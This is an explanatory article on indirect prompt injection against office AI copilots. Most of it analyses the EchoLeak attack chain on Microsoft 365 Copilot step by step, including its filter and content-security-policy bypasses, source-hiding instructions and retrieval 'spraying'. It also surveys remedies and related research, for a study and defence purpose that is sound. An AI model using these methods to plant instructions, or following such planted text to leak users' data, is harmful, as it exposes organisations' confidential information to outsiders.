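# Data theft through AI copilots in office software: how the flaws work, how they are fixed and how to design against them

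## What an office copilot can read, and why outside text can misdirect it

An office copilot is an AI assistant built into email, document and chat software. It answers questions and carries out small tasks using the user's emails, files and conversations. Microsoft sells one called Microsoft 365 Copilot, or simply Copilot, and Google, Slack and Salesforce offer similar assistants.

These assistants are useful because they can read so much, which also makes them worth attacking. An outsider who writes instructions into an ordinary email or a shared document can sometimes get the assistant to follow them, such as by collecting private data and sending it back. Security researchers use the word "exfiltration" for moving data out of an organisation to someone with no right to it. The attacker doesn't need a password or a virus. Microsoft (2025), in an account of its own defences, notes that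 even a plain text file can carry the instructions.

### One request, step by step

An employee of a company in the middle of a merger might ask Copilot to "summarise what I need to know about the merger". Copilot uses a large language model to write its answers, a program that produces text by predicting what comes next, using patterns from its training. The terms of a confidential merger were not in that training, so Copilot has to look them up before the model can write anything useful.

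The lookup goes through Microsoft Graph, the service that connects Microsoft 365 programs to an organisation's data. According to Microsoft's privacy documentation, Copilot draws on documents, emails, calendar, chats, meetings and contacts there, plus whatever the user is doing at the time, such as a meeting in progress.

Part of the search is ordinary keyword matching. The rest relies on what Microsoft calls a semantic index, which covers the user's mailbox and common file types, including Word, PowerPoint and PDF. The index represents text as vectors (lists of numbers) and places texts with similar meanings close together, so a question about the merger can bring up an email that mentions only "the acquisition". Closeness depends on the words, not on who wrote them, so a stranger's email about the merger may lie as near to the question as one from the finance director. Microsoft also ranks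 results by signals about the people a user works with, which presumably favors colleagues' material, but the stranger's email can still appear in the results.

Permissions then narrow the results. Copilot works on the user's behalf, and Microsoft describes both the index and the Graph queries as "security trimmed", meaning that if an employee cannot open the board minutes, the minutes do not reach the model. Microsoft tells outside developers that the programming interface for searching this index also trims results, at the time of each query. The check tests whether the user may read an item, so an unsolicited email in the user's own inbox passes.

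Copilot then adds the passages it has found to the employee's request and sends both to the language model. Searching a store of documents for relevant passages and adding them to the text that the model works from is called retrieval-augmented generation, or RAG. All the text that the model receives for one answer is its context. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, lists what Copilot's context contains: the chat history, whatever Copilot has fetched from the mailbox, OneDrive, SharePoint and Teams, and details loaded in advance, such as the names of the user and the organisation. The context also includes Microsoft's own system instructions. It can include text from the open web as well, because Copilot Chat can send search queries to Bing to improve an answer, according to Microsoft. For the merger question, the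 context might hold two paragraphs of a draft agreement, a Teams exchange about redundancies, a note from the company's lawyers and an email from a sender whom nobody in the company has met.

After the model writes its answer, Copilot consults Graph and the index again for post-processing. It then returns the text to Word, Outlook or Teams, along with any command for that program. Microsoft's architecture guide outlines this sequence. When the program displays the answer, it turns any formatting marks in the text into links and pictures. To show a picture from a web address, the user's browser has to contact that address.

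### No firm boundary between instructions and data

A person reading the assembled context would easily see that the employee's request is something to carry out and the lawyers' note is something to read. The model receives the whole context as a single sequence of tokens, which are the words and fragments of words that language models process.

*Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, an article by David C that the UK's National Cyber Security Centre published in December 2025, compares prompt injection with an older attack on databases. SQL is the language in which programs query databases. For years, attackers could type SQL commands into a web form and have the database run them, because careless programs pasted the form's contents straight into a query. The fix was the parameterised query, which sends the command and the form's contents to the database separately,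 so that the database treats whatever the attacker types only as data. A language model has no equivalent safeguard, because its only operation is to predict the next token from all the tokens so far, any of which may influence the prediction.

Many models receive their context with labels that mark each stretch of text as the system's instructions, the user's words or material fetched by a tool. Training teaches the models to act on the user's words and only consult the fetched material. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) measured how these labels affect a model's internal activity. The researchers wrapped identical passages of web text in each label in turn and trained a probe, a small classifier, to infer the label from that activity. Because the passages were identical, the probe could learn only from the effect of the label itself. The researchers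 then took 200 real conversations and put the users' words under the label for fetched material. In all four models examined, the style of the text outweighed its label, and the probe still attributed the words to the user with an average probability of 76 to 88 per cent.

In 1,000 trials, the same researchers had an AI agent summarise web pages in which they had planted a command to send out a private file. They kept the command fixed and varied only the text around it. The attack worked 2 per cent of the time when the command scored as least user-like on the probe, and 70 per cent when it scored as most user-like. The probes covered models of 20 to 120 billion parameters, so the largest commercial models may not behave the same way.

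Models can ignore planted commands even though this boundary is missing. In another experiment by Ye and colleagues, plainly worded planted commands succeeded 0 to 2 per cent of the time against every model but one, where they succeeded 26 per cent of the time. When the researchers added text in the style of the model's own reasoning, success rose to between 56 and 70 per cent. So a model can learn to resist familiar attacks, but this resistance is a statistical habit that a change of wording may defeat. *From AI-Generated Content to Agentic Action* (2026) likewise contrasts models, which resolve conflicting instructions by learned rules of thumb, with older software, which would apply a hard constraint.

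*Can LLMs Separate Instructions From Data?* (Zverev et al., 2025) proposed a formal measure of this separation and a data set for testing it. *ASIDE* (2025), a later paper on building the separation into a model's architecture, describes the procedure. The test has 9,160 pairs, each with an instruction and some data for it. The tester inserts an unrelated instruction into the instruction half of a pair, then into the data half, and compares the outputs. A model scores well if it follows the inserted instruction in the first case and ignores it in the second.

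David C thinks there is a good chance that nobody will ever close this gap the way parameterised queries closed the one in SQL. Ye and colleagues are somewhat more hopeful, and treat cleanly separating roles inside the model as an open research problem. Microsoft calls the risk inherent in modern language models, and its guide *Defend against indirect prompt injection attacks* advises developers to design systems on the expectation that some attacks will succeed.

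### Direct and indirect prompt injection

Attacks that exploit this gap are called prompt injection. In May 2022, the security firm Preamble privately reported the flaw in GPT-3, then OpenAI's leading language model. It made its report public that September in *Declassifying the Responsible Disclosure of the Prompt Injection Attack Vulnerability of GPT-3* (2022). The programmer Simon Willison coined the term the same year, by analogy with SQL injection.

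Early work studied direct prompt injection, where the attacker types the prompt. *Ignore Previous Prompt* (Perez and Ribeiro, 2022) showed that simple handwritten inputs could divert GPT-3 from the task its developers had set (goal hijacking) or make it reveal their hidden instructions (prompt leaking). Direct injection gains an attacker fairly little against an office copilot, because only the organisation's own people can type into its Copilot, and Copilot retrieves only what they could open themselves.

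Indirect prompt injection removes that limit because the attacker plants instructions in content that the model will read later, while working for somebody else. Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) introduced the idea in *Not what you've signed up for* and tried it on Microsoft's Bing Chat, code-completion tools and their own test applications. They argued that retrieval blurs the line between data and instructions, so that processing an untrusted document comes close to running an untrusted program. They distinguished passive delivery, where the attacker leaves the text for a search to pick up, from active delivery, such as sending it by email. Their list of new products already included Microsoft 365 Copilot. They thought an attacker could email instructions that a personal assistant would read and follow, looking up personal data and sending messages.

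David C gives the everyday example of a recruiter who asks a model to score CVs, where one candidate has hidden a line in their CV telling the model to approve it. In the merger example, the stranger's email would contain, among plausible remarks on the timetable, sentences that the model takes for part of its task. Asking Copilot about the merger may be enough to bring the email into the context, even if the employee never opened it.

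Microsoft calls indirect injection a cross-prompt injection attack (XPIA). Many people confuse prompt injection with jailbreaking, which means persuading a model to break its safety rules and produce forbidden content. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, thinks this confusion is harmful because developers who equate the two conclude that an embarrassing answer is the model vendor's problem and overlook a flaw that exposes their own users' data.

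### The confused deputy

The underlying pattern is older than language models. *The Confused Deputy*, an essay Hardy wrote in the late 1980s, describes an incident at Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time. Customers could tell the compiler, a program that translates source code, which file to write debugging output to. The compiler also had its own permission to write in its home directory, which held its usage statistics and the company's billing records. One customer named the billing file. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission to write in that directory, and the compiler overwrote the bills.

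The customer had no right to access that file, but the compiler did, for another purpose. The compiler had no way to indicate which of its two authorities it was using for a given write. A program like this, which has rights and can be directed by someone who lacks them, is called a confused deputy.

Copilot fits the description closely. It acts with the employee's rights, which the author of the planted email lacks. Every permission check succeeds because it tests the employee's rights. Microsoft is correct that an injection can reach only what the user can reach, and this limit is useful because an attack through a junior clerk's Copilot will not expose the whole company's files. But a finance director in the middle of a merger can reach most of what a thief would want.

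Hardy's remedy was to require the compiler to present the specific authority for each write. A conventional program can do this because its programmer knows whom each line of code serves. But a language model's output comes from its whole context, and nobody can say with certainty which sentence in the context produced which sentence in the answer. David C therefore calls language models "inherently confusable" deputies and says designers can reduce and contain the risk but not remove it.

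Ravia, who led the research at the security group Aim Labs, proposed the narrower term "LLM scope violation" for cases where instructions from an untrusted source make the model use trusted data in its context without the user's explicit consent. The copilot may summarize the stranger's email, but the email should not determine what happens to the draft agreement beside it. Ravia compares the email to a program with few permissions that reaches protected files through another program with many.

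In a post on Aim Labs' findings, Willison (2025) objected that the new term described a familiar pattern, in which a model cannot take account of where its tokens came from once they are in a single sequence. Willison is surely right about the cause. Ravia's reason for the term is practical. Programmers had long known about buffer overflows, in which a program writes past the end of its allotted memory, and having a separate name for one type, stack overflows, helped them build a specific protection against it. Similarly, "scope violation" names something a defence could look for, which is the use of outside text to get at inside data, even when the text looks harmless. The term is useful for that purpose, as long as nobody takes it to mean a different underlying problem.

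### The lethal trifecta

A misdirected assistant does not necessarily leak anything. If the planted email only makes Copilot write a bad summary, the employee is misinformed but the merger terms stay private. Theft becomes possible when an assistant has access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and some way to communicate with the outside, a combination Willison calls the "lethal trifecta".

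An office copilot is designed to read private data. It is also exposed to untrusted content, because anyone who knows or guesses an employee's email address can put text in the mailbox it reads. In *EchoLeak*, a case study of one Copilot flaw, Reddy and Gujral (2025) assume an attacker who has no account and no access to Copilot, and can only send content to the organisation. They assume only that the victim is an employee who occasionally asks Copilot a work question.

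Stolen data can leave through features that people want, such as the links and pictures in an assistant's answers. Microsoft describes how attackers can use either one. The planted instructions have the model write a web address that includes the stolen text, and the attacker's server receives the text when the browser requests that address. The browser loads a picture automatically, while a link needs a click. Assistants that can use tools may also write the data somewhere public, or leak it one bit at a time if an outsider can observe whether a particular tool ran.

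Vendors can do the most about this third condition. Microsoft reports that it removes unnecessary exits from Copilot and requires the user's approval for actions such as sending an email. Willison lists more than a dozen products with flaws of this type and observes that vendors nearly always fixed them by closing the exit. The other two conditions are much harder to remove, because a copilot that could not read the mailbox, or that ignored all mail from outside the company, would be little help to someone negotiating with another firm.

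### What this flaw is not

Companies also worry about other ways AI tools might leak confidential data, and these need different remedies. One is that staff paste confidential material into a chatbot. The user then discloses the data, knowingly or not, and no attacker has to misdirect the tool. Microsoft's *AI Application Security Series 1* treats passwords and proprietary code in prompts as a data risk, and lists malicious instructions in documents under a separate heading.

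Oversharing is a permissions problem. For example, an employee who moves to another department but keeps access to the old one's files may find Copilot quoting from them. The settings allow this, and the data stays inside the company, but loose permissions increase what an attacker could steal through a later injection.

Models can also repeat their training data. *The Prompt Report* (2024), a survey of prompting techniques, cites 2021 work by Carlini and colleagues on prompts that extract private information a model memorised during training. The merger documents, by contrast, are exposed because Copilot places them in the context for a single answer. Microsoft states that it does not use prompts, answers or Graph data to train the foundation models behind Copilot, but this does not protect documents placed in the context.

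Researchers grade injection flaws partly by how much the victim has to do. A one-click attack needs the victim to open one link or press one button, while a zero-click attack needs only ordinary use of the assistant, such as the question about the merger. The software industry identifies publicly known security flaws by CVE (Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures) numbers. EchoLeak, the zero-click flaw in Copilot that Ravia's group reported to Microsoft in January 2025, is CVE-2025-32711. The Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS) rates a flaw's severity from 0 to 10.

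## EchoLeak: a complete attack, step by step

EchoLeak began with an email to an employee and ended with that employee's data in the log of an attacker's web server. Ravia counts four protections that the attack had to bypass: a classifier that screened incoming text for planted instructions, a filter that removed outside links from Copilot's answers, a list of sites from which the browser could load images, and the references that Copilot gives to its sources. Aim Labs bypassed them one at a time, producing several versions of the attack. The early versions required the victim to click or accept something, but the last did not. Microsoft repaired the flaw on its own servers before Aim Labs published the details in June 2025.

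### An email written for its human reader

Microsoft's XPIA classifiers are filters meant to catch indirect prompt injections before they reach the language model. Reddy and Gujral suppose that such a filter would flag a crude message that greets Copilot by name and tells it to ignore its previous instructions. Aim Labs' email never mentioned Copilot, assistants or AI, and its instructions read as if they were meant for the person who received the email.

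Ravia attributes the failure partly to a lack of training data. Planted instructions can come in any language or tone and on any subject, so a classifier needs many examples to learn from, and good collections of real attacks are scarce. More data probably wouldn't solve the problem, though, because ordinary business email is also full of instructions. An attacker and a finance director could use the same words to ask for a project's confidential figures to be compiled. Ravia accepts that this makes detection inherently difficult, though not hopeless.

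Once past the classifier, the email sat in the employee's mailbox. To make Copilot likely to retrieve it, Aim Labs had written it as one long message with sections on common subjects such as onboarding and leave, and had repeated the instructions in each section. When the employee asked about one of those subjects, Copilot added the matching section to its context along with the company's own material.

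The key sentence in the instructions told the reader to take the most sensitive information from the context, including earlier messages, and use it as part of a web address. This was the scope violation, which Ravia considers the core red flag of the attack. Because the model selected the most sensitive information itself, an attacker who had never heard of the merger could still steal its terms.

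### From a link to an image

The attacker could now get the model to follow instructions but had no way to receive anything from it. Aim Labs' first idea was to send the data out through a link. Copilot writes its answers in Markdown, a plain-text notation that chat programs convert into headings, links and pictures. A Markdown link usually has the visible words in square brackets, followed directly by the address in round ones. If the address pointed to the attacker's server and included the stolen text, a click would record that text in the server's log.

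Microsoft had anticipated this. Copilot removed links from an answer before the user could click on them, unless they led to approved internal pages. But Markdown also has reference-style links, in which the visible words carry a short label and the address sits on a separate line next to the same label. These look identical to ordinary links when displayed. Copilot's filter missed them, and Ravia lists several variants that also got through. Willison (2025) thinks Microsoft forgot to apply its filter to the lesser-known notation.

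This is an old kind of mistake in web security. One program checked the text and another displayed it, and the two used different rules for what counts as a link. A filter that examined the links after the conversion from Markdown would presumably not have had this gap.

The reference-style link gave Aim Labs its first complete chain, a one-click attack. The employee would ask an ordinary question and get an ordinary-looking answer from a trusted tool. Some employees might then follow the link in the answer, but many would not bother.

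In Markdown, an exclamation mark in front of a link turns it into an image, which the browser loads without a click. Copilot's filter checked images as well as links, but it missed reference-style images just as it missed reference-style links. This would have made the attack zero-click, but the browser blocked requests to the attacker's site.

### Past the list of allowed sites

The browser refused because of Copilot's content security policy (CSP), the list of sites from which a web page allows the browser to load images and other content. The image list on Copilot's page had about thirty entries. Many were broad, covering every address under SharePoint, Teams or Bing, but none covered the attacker's site.

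Aim Labs could therefore make the victim's browser request any address on an approved domain, but not on any other. This was of little use by itself, because the stolen text would go to Microsoft. Ravia explains that the browser expected an image, so it would not follow a redirect to an outside address or run any code that the site sent back. The researchers needed a service on an approved domain whose own server would fetch an outside address on request, a weakness known as server-side request forgery (SSRF).

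Aim Labs first tried SharePoint, which hosts websites for organisations and where an attacker can set up a site like anyone else. Microsoft had already closed the obvious routes. Site owners can no longer add code that runs on SharePoint's servers, or pass the end of a web address to an automated workflow behind the page. Aim Labs then found a SharePoint service that fetches outside content from a given address and embeds it in a page. The browser would contact SharePoint, which the policy allowed, and SharePoint would contact the attacker's server with the secret in the address.

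This completed the chain without requiring the victim to click a link, but it worked only if the victim had connected to their SharePoint account and accepted the attacker's invitation to view the site. Staff learn to ignore invitations from unknown companies, and a wary employee or the company's security team could notice the invitation before any data had left.

Microsoft Teams offered a better route. One of its addresses, which Reddy and Gujral describe as part of a preview service, would also fetch any outside address it was given. This route required no invitation, and the victim had to do nothing beyond asking Copilot a question. The browser then loaded what appeared to be a Teams picture, the Teams server requested the attacker's address, and the stolen text appeared in the attacker's log.

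Willison calls the Teams address an open redirect, a page that forwards the browser to any destination named in the link. Ravia's account suggests something different, because the browser would not have followed a redirect. Reddy and Gujral also class the step as server-side request forgery, in which a server is made to fetch an address for the attacker. The distinction matters for blocking such an attack, because checking the sites a browser visits will reveal only Microsoft's.

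### Hiding the source

Copilot normally lists the emails and files an answer draws on, so an employee who checked the list might have noticed the attacker's email. To prevent this, the attacker wrote in the email that its "recipient" must never refer to it, for compliance reasons, and Copilot left it out. This worked because Microsoft relied on the model to name its sources, and the attacker was already giving the model instructions.

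Reddy and Gujral think the victim would have seen at most what looked like a broken image or link. This would have given the attacker more time, and perhaps the chance to repeat the theft whenever a later question brought up the email.

### What could leak and what could not

Anything in the model's context could leak. Ravia says the attack worked both on a single question and in a longer conversation. If an employee spent the morning asking Copilot about redundancies and then asked about parental leave, an attacker could have obtained the morning's answers. SecurityWeek's *‘EchoLeak’ AI Attack Enabled Theft of Sensitive Data via Microsoft 365 Copilot* describes the data at risk as information from the victim's prior chats, but the attack also exposed whatever Copilot had fetched.

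The attack could not reach material that Copilot had not placed in the context, or anything the employee had no permission to open. Reddy and Gujral write that the email could coerce Copilot into accessing internal files. This seems to go further than Ravia's account, in which the employee's own questions bring files into the context and the email only selects from what is there. Web addresses also have a practical length limit, so a single answer would more likely have leaked a password or a paragraph than a whole contract.

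In the conclusion, Ravia describes a complete compromise of Copilot's "data integrity". Security specialists use "integrity" to mean protection against alteration. The published steps copy data without altering it, so the victim lost confidentiality rather than integrity. The attacker did not gain control of the account or run any program on the victim's computer.

The attack's reliability is hard to judge. Ravia reports that Copilot retrieved the email in response to questions on various topics, but gives no figure for how often this happened or how often the model then followed the email's instructions.

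### How far the "first zero-click" claim holds

Aim Labs calls EchoLeak the first zero-click AI vulnerability in its headline, but defines the claim more narrowly in the article. There, EchoLeak is the first vulnerability in a widely used generative AI product to centre on a flaw in the AI, require no specific user behaviour and put no restriction on what data can leave. These qualifications are needed because researchers had already been stealing data through AI-written images and links for two years.

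In April 2023, Roman Samoilenko showed that ChatGPT could leak a conversation through a single-pixel image. According to Willison (2023), the attacker's website added hidden instructions to any text a visitor copied from it. The victim then had to paste that text into ChatGPT.

That same month, security researcher Johann Rehberger reported a similar flaw to Microsoft. In the attack described in *Bing Chat*, a post on his blog Embrace The Red, a comment or advertisement on a web page took over the assistant, which then loaded an image whose address contained a summary of the page and the conversation. The victim had to open that page and start chatting with Bing there. Microsoft's fix seems to have included a content security policy that allowed images from only four Bing addresses, a much tighter list than the one Aim Labs later found on Copilot's page.

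The nearest precedent is an attack that Rehberger reported to Google in September 2023, after Google's assistant Bard gained access to users' documents and email. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* describes how instructions planted in a shared Google document made Bard write an image address containing the opening words of the conversation. Google's policy blocked images from outside sites but allowed everything under google.com, so Rehberger used a Google service open to anyone to host a small script there, which saved whatever arrived in the address. The Bard attack thus already used an image that loads by itself and a detour through the vendor's own trusted domain. Rehberger labelled the image step "zero click", but in the demonstration the victim brought the malicious document into the chat. Google confirmed a fix within a month.

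Copilot had also leaked data before EchoLeak. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* recounts an attack from early 2024 in which a malicious email made Copilot search for other emails and hide their text, as invisible characters, inside a link. The victim had to use Copilot on the malicious email and then click the link. Michael Bargury of the security firm Zenity demonstrated another attack later that year. According to Willison, it started when the user asked Copilot to summarise the attacker's email, and it also required a click. Copilot checked whether Microsoft's quarterly earnings had passed a certain figure and offered one of two links depending on the answer, so the attacker learned only a yes or no from the click. Ravia may have meant cases like this when writing that some earlier attacks put very strong restrictions on the stolen data.

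Bargury's firm, Zenity, disputed the claim that EchoLeak was new. In *EchoLeak: A Reminder That AI Agent Risks Are Here to Stay*, Zenity Labs (2025) argued that researchers had known the techniques for 12 to 24 months. The only new element it acknowledged was the bypass of Copilot's filter on Markdown images. Zenity and Aim both sold protection against such attacks, so both had a commercial interest in who was first.

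The headline is overstated, but the narrower definition still holds when EchoLeak is compared with these earlier attacks. In each of them, the victim had to direct the assistant to the attacker's text or click on something, and often both. In EchoLeak, the victim could trigger the attack by asking about parental leave, without ever having seen the attacker's email.

According to SecurityWeek, the attack starts when the user asks Copilot for information that the malicious email refers to. In a Hacker News thread, several programmers argued that a flaw which depends on a prompt from the user should be called "low interaction" at best, not "zero-click". Another replied that "zero-click" refers to contact with the malicious content, and compared asking Copilot a question to logging in to a computer, which nobody counts as a click. A user named wunderwuzzi23, Rehberger's handle, agreed that the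 term fitted but disputed that EchoLeak was the first flaw it applied to. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) notes that the official vulnerability records describe a flaw that requires no user interaction, which matches the looser use of "zero-click".

That seems fair for a product built to answer questions, since even a careful employee would have no reason to avoid asking one. But EchoLeak didn't succeed as soon as the email arrived, as the term can suggest. The message had to get through the spam filter, Copilot had to retrieve it in response to a later question, and the model had to follow the instructions in it, so a company that paid for Copilot but never used it would have lost nothing.

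### Which controls broke, and which remedies would have held

Reddy and Gujral matched each step to the security controls it defeated, using standard catalogues such as the one the US standards body NIST publishes for government systems. They worked from public accounts about two months after the disclosure and did not reproduce the attack. In their mapping, the email got past the checks on incoming data, the link and the image got past the controls on where information may flow, and the Teams address exploited a trusted server. They placed the instruction not to cite the email under audit records, since an answer with a missing source gives investigators less evidence.

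Reddy and Gujral's most useful entry covers a step where the attacker had nothing to bypass. When Copilot retrieved the email, it placed a stranger's text beside internal documents, as Microsoft had designed it to do. They count this as a breach of least privilege, the principle that a program should have only the access its task requires.

They also judged whether each of eight remedies would stop zero-click theft. They call the result theoretical and state elsewhere that they ran no experiments, although one line refers to "our tests". The verdicts are best read as reasoning, not as test results, and some look too generous or too harsh given the details of the attack chain.

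| Remedy | Reddy and Gujral: does it stop zero-click theft? | What it would have taken against EchoLeak |
|---|---|---|
| Tag outside text in the context | No | A model that reliably obeys the tags |
| Use only internal sources by default | No | Keeping the email away from internal files and from the chat history |
| Limit answers to approved formatting | No | A rule that drops images altogether |
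| Allow only approved web addresses | Yes | A check of the whole address, beyond its domain |
| Strict content security policy | Yes | Leaving the Teams service off the list |
| Signed image proxy | Yes | Refusing to sign addresses that the model has written |
| Human approval for outside content | Yes | Showing the user the real destination |
| Monitoring of outgoing data | No | Sight of the address before the browser requests it |

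A strict content security policy would have stopped the zero-click version if it had excluded every site that would fetch outside addresses for a stranger. Reddy and Gujral advise allowing only the company's own domains, with no entries that cover a whole family of addresses, but this could still have allowed Teams, which is one of Microsoft's own domains. Checking how each approved site behaves is hard when the list has about thirty entries run by many different product teams. The difficulty was still there in December 2026, when the same research group, by then part of Cato Networks, published three more zero-click chains in Copilot. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) presents them as a sequel. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) reports that Microsoft has patched all three and that one of them sent data out through an image address that Bing fetched.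 Bing was already on the list of approved sites that Aim Labs had printed the year before.

An image policy also does not restrict links, so the attacker could have gone back to the one-click version. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* quotes Google's statement that its assistant Gemini does not display external images, so EchoLeak's image step would not work there. But Checkmarx found that a link carrying data in its address still worked in Gemini once the user clicked it.

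The list of approved addresses should have been judged more cautiously. In the final version of EchoLeak, the attacker's address was inside a Teams address, so a check on the domain alone would have matched a Microsoft domain and allowed the request. Asking for the user's approval has the same weakness, because an employee asked whether Copilot may load a picture from Teams will probably agree.

A signed proxy is more promising. This server fetches an image only if the address has a valid cryptographic signature and has not expired. The model cannot forge a signature, so the proxy would reject an address the model made up by following the attacker's instructions. This protection would be lost if another part of Copilot automatically signed every image address in an answer.

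Tagging outside text relies on the model to treat everything between two markers as having no authority. In experiments by Ye and colleagues, the style of a passage affected the model more than its label did, which gives little reason to expect a model to comply every time. Reddy and Gujral rightly describe tagging as insufficient on its own.

The paper contradicts itself on the most fundamental remedy, which is to answer from internal sources unless the user explicitly asks for outside ones. According to its text, EchoLeak would fail by design if Copilot never used emails from unknown senders to answer questions about internal projects, but its table lists zero-click theft as still succeeding. The text is closer to the truth, since instructions that never enter the context can't steer the model. They could still enter it through the chat history, however. If an employee discussed a confidential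 draft agreement in the morning and asked for a summary of outside mail in the afternoon, the planted instructions and the secret would be in the same conversation. To close this gap, Copilot would have to start a fresh context whenever it brought in outside mail, and it could then no longer compare the other side's latest offer with the company's own draft.

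## How an attacker's text reaches the assistant

EchoLeak arrived by email, but an attacker can plant instructions in anything a copilot reads. Most planted instructions stay in a mailbox or file store until a search retrieves them, so the attacker has to get the search to pick a planted passage over the genuine material there. A link that carries a prompt doesn't depend on a search, but the victim has to click it.

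### Places to leave text

Unread email is the easiest route for an outsider, who needs only an employee's address. The employee sets off the attack by asking the copilot a question, and sees nothing except perhaps one more unread message. Faisal reports that the victim never opened the email in any of Simonovich's three ReLeak chains. The choice of address matters a little, because Microsoft says Copilot's semantic index covers a user's own mailbox but not shared, delegated or archived ones. A message to a general enquiries address is therefore presumably less useful to an attacker than one to the finance director.

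An attacker can also hide instructions in a shared document, in white text on a white page or in type too small to notice. Readers are unlikely to notice this text in Word, but software that extracts text for an index usually collects every character, whatever its colour. Microsoft (2026), in a study of attempts to manipulate AI assistants, lists documents with hidden instructions as one method of attack. The victim can trigger the attack just by asking the assistant a question that the document seems to answer.

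Getting the file into the right place is harder than sending an email. Microsoft adds new SharePoint files to Copilot's organisation-wide index daily if at least two people can open the site they are on. A company-wide sharing link does not put a file in that index. The file joins an employee's personal index only when that employee opens the link. An outsider therefore usually needs someone inside to open or save the file, as an employee might do with a supplier's brochure. Once the brochure is in the merger folder, it counts as an internal document, and a rule restricting Copilot to internal sources would no longer exclude it.

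An attacker can send someone a calendar invitation almost as easily as an email. The sender writes the title and description, and some calendar programs add the meeting before the recipient accepts it, though the victim may notice an unfamiliar appointment. Asking the assistant what is on tomorrow's calendar could be enough to bring the description into its context. Because the assistant finds the entry by date, the attacker doesn't have to guess which subject the victim will ask about. Researchers have used invitations this way against Google's Gemini.

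Anyone who can publish a web page, or comment on someone else's, can plant text for an assistant that reads the web. Microsoft warns that reputable sites may carry injections in their forums and user reviews. The victim has to ask for a summary of the page, or ask something that leads the assistant to it, but doesn't see the hidden text. The United Nations University (UNU) describes the use of hidden page text in CoSnitch, an attack on the consumer version of Copilot. Microsoft patched the flaw in August 2026.

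Connected services are the least visible route. Organisations can use Microsoft's Copilot connectors to bring material from other companies' software into Microsoft Graph, where Copilot can search it. The connectors preserve the rules on who may read each record, but those rules don't stop an outsider from writing instructions into one. If a company connects its customer-support system, for example, a member of the public could put instructions in a complaint. An employee who later asked Copilot about recent complaints would see that complaint as a record from the company's own system.

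### How a search selects passages

Whether any of this text reaches the model depends on the search. The vectors in a semantic index come from an embedding model, which typically turns each passage into several hundred to a few thousand numbers and treats the user's question in the same way. The search then compares the directions of the two vectors. The usual measure, cosine similarity, divides their dot product by the product of their lengths:

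cos(u, v) = (u · v) / (|u| |v|)

The result ranges from −1 to 1, where 1 means that both vectors point the same way. For example, (3, 4) and (4, 3) have a dot product of 24 and each has length 5, so their similarity is 24/25, or 0.96. The dot product of (3, 4) and (4, −3) is 0, so their similarity is also 0.

The search gives the assistant only the few passages with the highest scores, perhaps five, so a planted passage has to score higher than genuine ones to be included. A similarity score of 0.7 might be more than enough on a subject the company has never written about, but far too low on one covered by a detailed company manual.

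Embedding models accept a limited amount of text at once, often a few hundred words, so systems split long documents into chunks and give each chunk its own vector. This helps honest users, because the vector for a chunk about parental leave is closer to a question about parental leave than a single vector for the whole staff handbook would be. It also gives an attacker who sends a long email many chances to match a user's question.

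### RAG spraying

Ravia calls the deliberate use of those chances "RAG spraying". An attacker does better to scatter points widely in the space of vectors, by sending many emails or one long email that the system will split. Aim Labs used one long email for EchoLeak. An attacker could instead research the target and write one email on the subject the employee seems most likely to raise, but that email would occupy a single point and match few questions.

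To estimate how much this could help, suppose that each of n chunks has a chance p of being retrieved for a random question. If the chunks succeed or fail independently, they all miss with probability (1 − p)^n, so the model reads at least one with probability 1 − (1 − p)^n.

Aim Labs published no retrieval rates, so the value of p here is illustrative. If p is 2 per cent, the chance that at least one of ten independent chunks is retrieved is 1 − 0.98^10, or about 18 per cent. The table compares this with the two extremes.

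| Number of chunks | Every chunk matches the same questions | Chunks are independent | No two chunks match the same question |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 2% | 2% | 2% |
| 10 | 2% | 18% | 20% |
| 30 | 2% | 45% | 60% |
| 50 | 2% | 64% | 100% |

Real chunks are not retrieved independently of one another. Those in the EchoLeak email shared the same block of instructions, which would tend to make their vectors similar and bring them up for the same questions, though their different headings would push the vectors apart. Sending fifty copies of one paragraph instead of one would barely raise the chance of retrieval, while sending fifty paragraphs on unrelated subjects could raise it slightly more than the formula predicts. The chance p also varies, since a chunk on a subject that the company has covered thoroughly competes with more chunks.

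The attacker's odds also improve over time, as a person asks more questions. Five questions put to ten chunks give 50 chances, and on the same assumptions the total probability is again 64 per cent. This figure is probably too high, because one person's questions tend to resemble each other.

Aim Labs had hoped to spread the chunks more cleverly. An embedding model and a language model process text differently, so adding a few random characters or replacing an s with a 5 might move a passage's vector a long way while leaving the passage readable to the language model. Ravia tested the effect on vectors with OpenAI's embedding model text-embedding-ada-002 and found that the similarity between a text and its altered copy could fall as low as 0.7.

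A score of 0.7 is low for this model. "Greeting card messages" and "Exploring philosophy of science" scored above 0.7, so the altered copy was less similar to its original than those two phrases were to each other. However, 0.7 is the lowest score Ravia reports and doesn't show the typical effect. Aim Labs could not use the trick against Copilot because Microsoft has not disclosed which embedding model it uses, so the researchers could not calculate the altered chunks' embeddings. They used plain headings about common staff questions instead, which was enough.

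### The retrieval barrier

Many laboratory tests of indirect injection skip retrieval. The researchers put the malicious text straight into the context, or have the user ask about the "latest email" when that email is the malicious one. In *Overcoming the Retrieval Barrier*, Chang, Bao and colleagues (2026) asked whether a system would retrieve planted text when people asked ordinary questions of a realistic collection.

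The researchers used 11 collections from BEIR, a standard benchmark for search systems, with material including web passages, financial questions and scientific abstracts. The collections ranged from about 26,000 to 8.8 million documents. For each of 100 questions per collection, they added one malicious item and checked whether it appeared in the top five results. Items with no special preparation never appeared there.

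They then split the planted text into an "attack fragment", which held the instructions, and a short "trigger fragment" in front of it, which served only to make the text more similar to one chosen question. To find a trigger, their program generated 5,000 random strings of ten tokens, scored each through the embedding model's public interface, and kept the best fifth. It then made the tokens in those strings more likely in the next batch, and repeated this for 30 rounds. This procedure, the cross-entropy method, doesn't require access to the embedding model's internals. It cost 21 cents per question on OpenAI's text-embedding-3-small.

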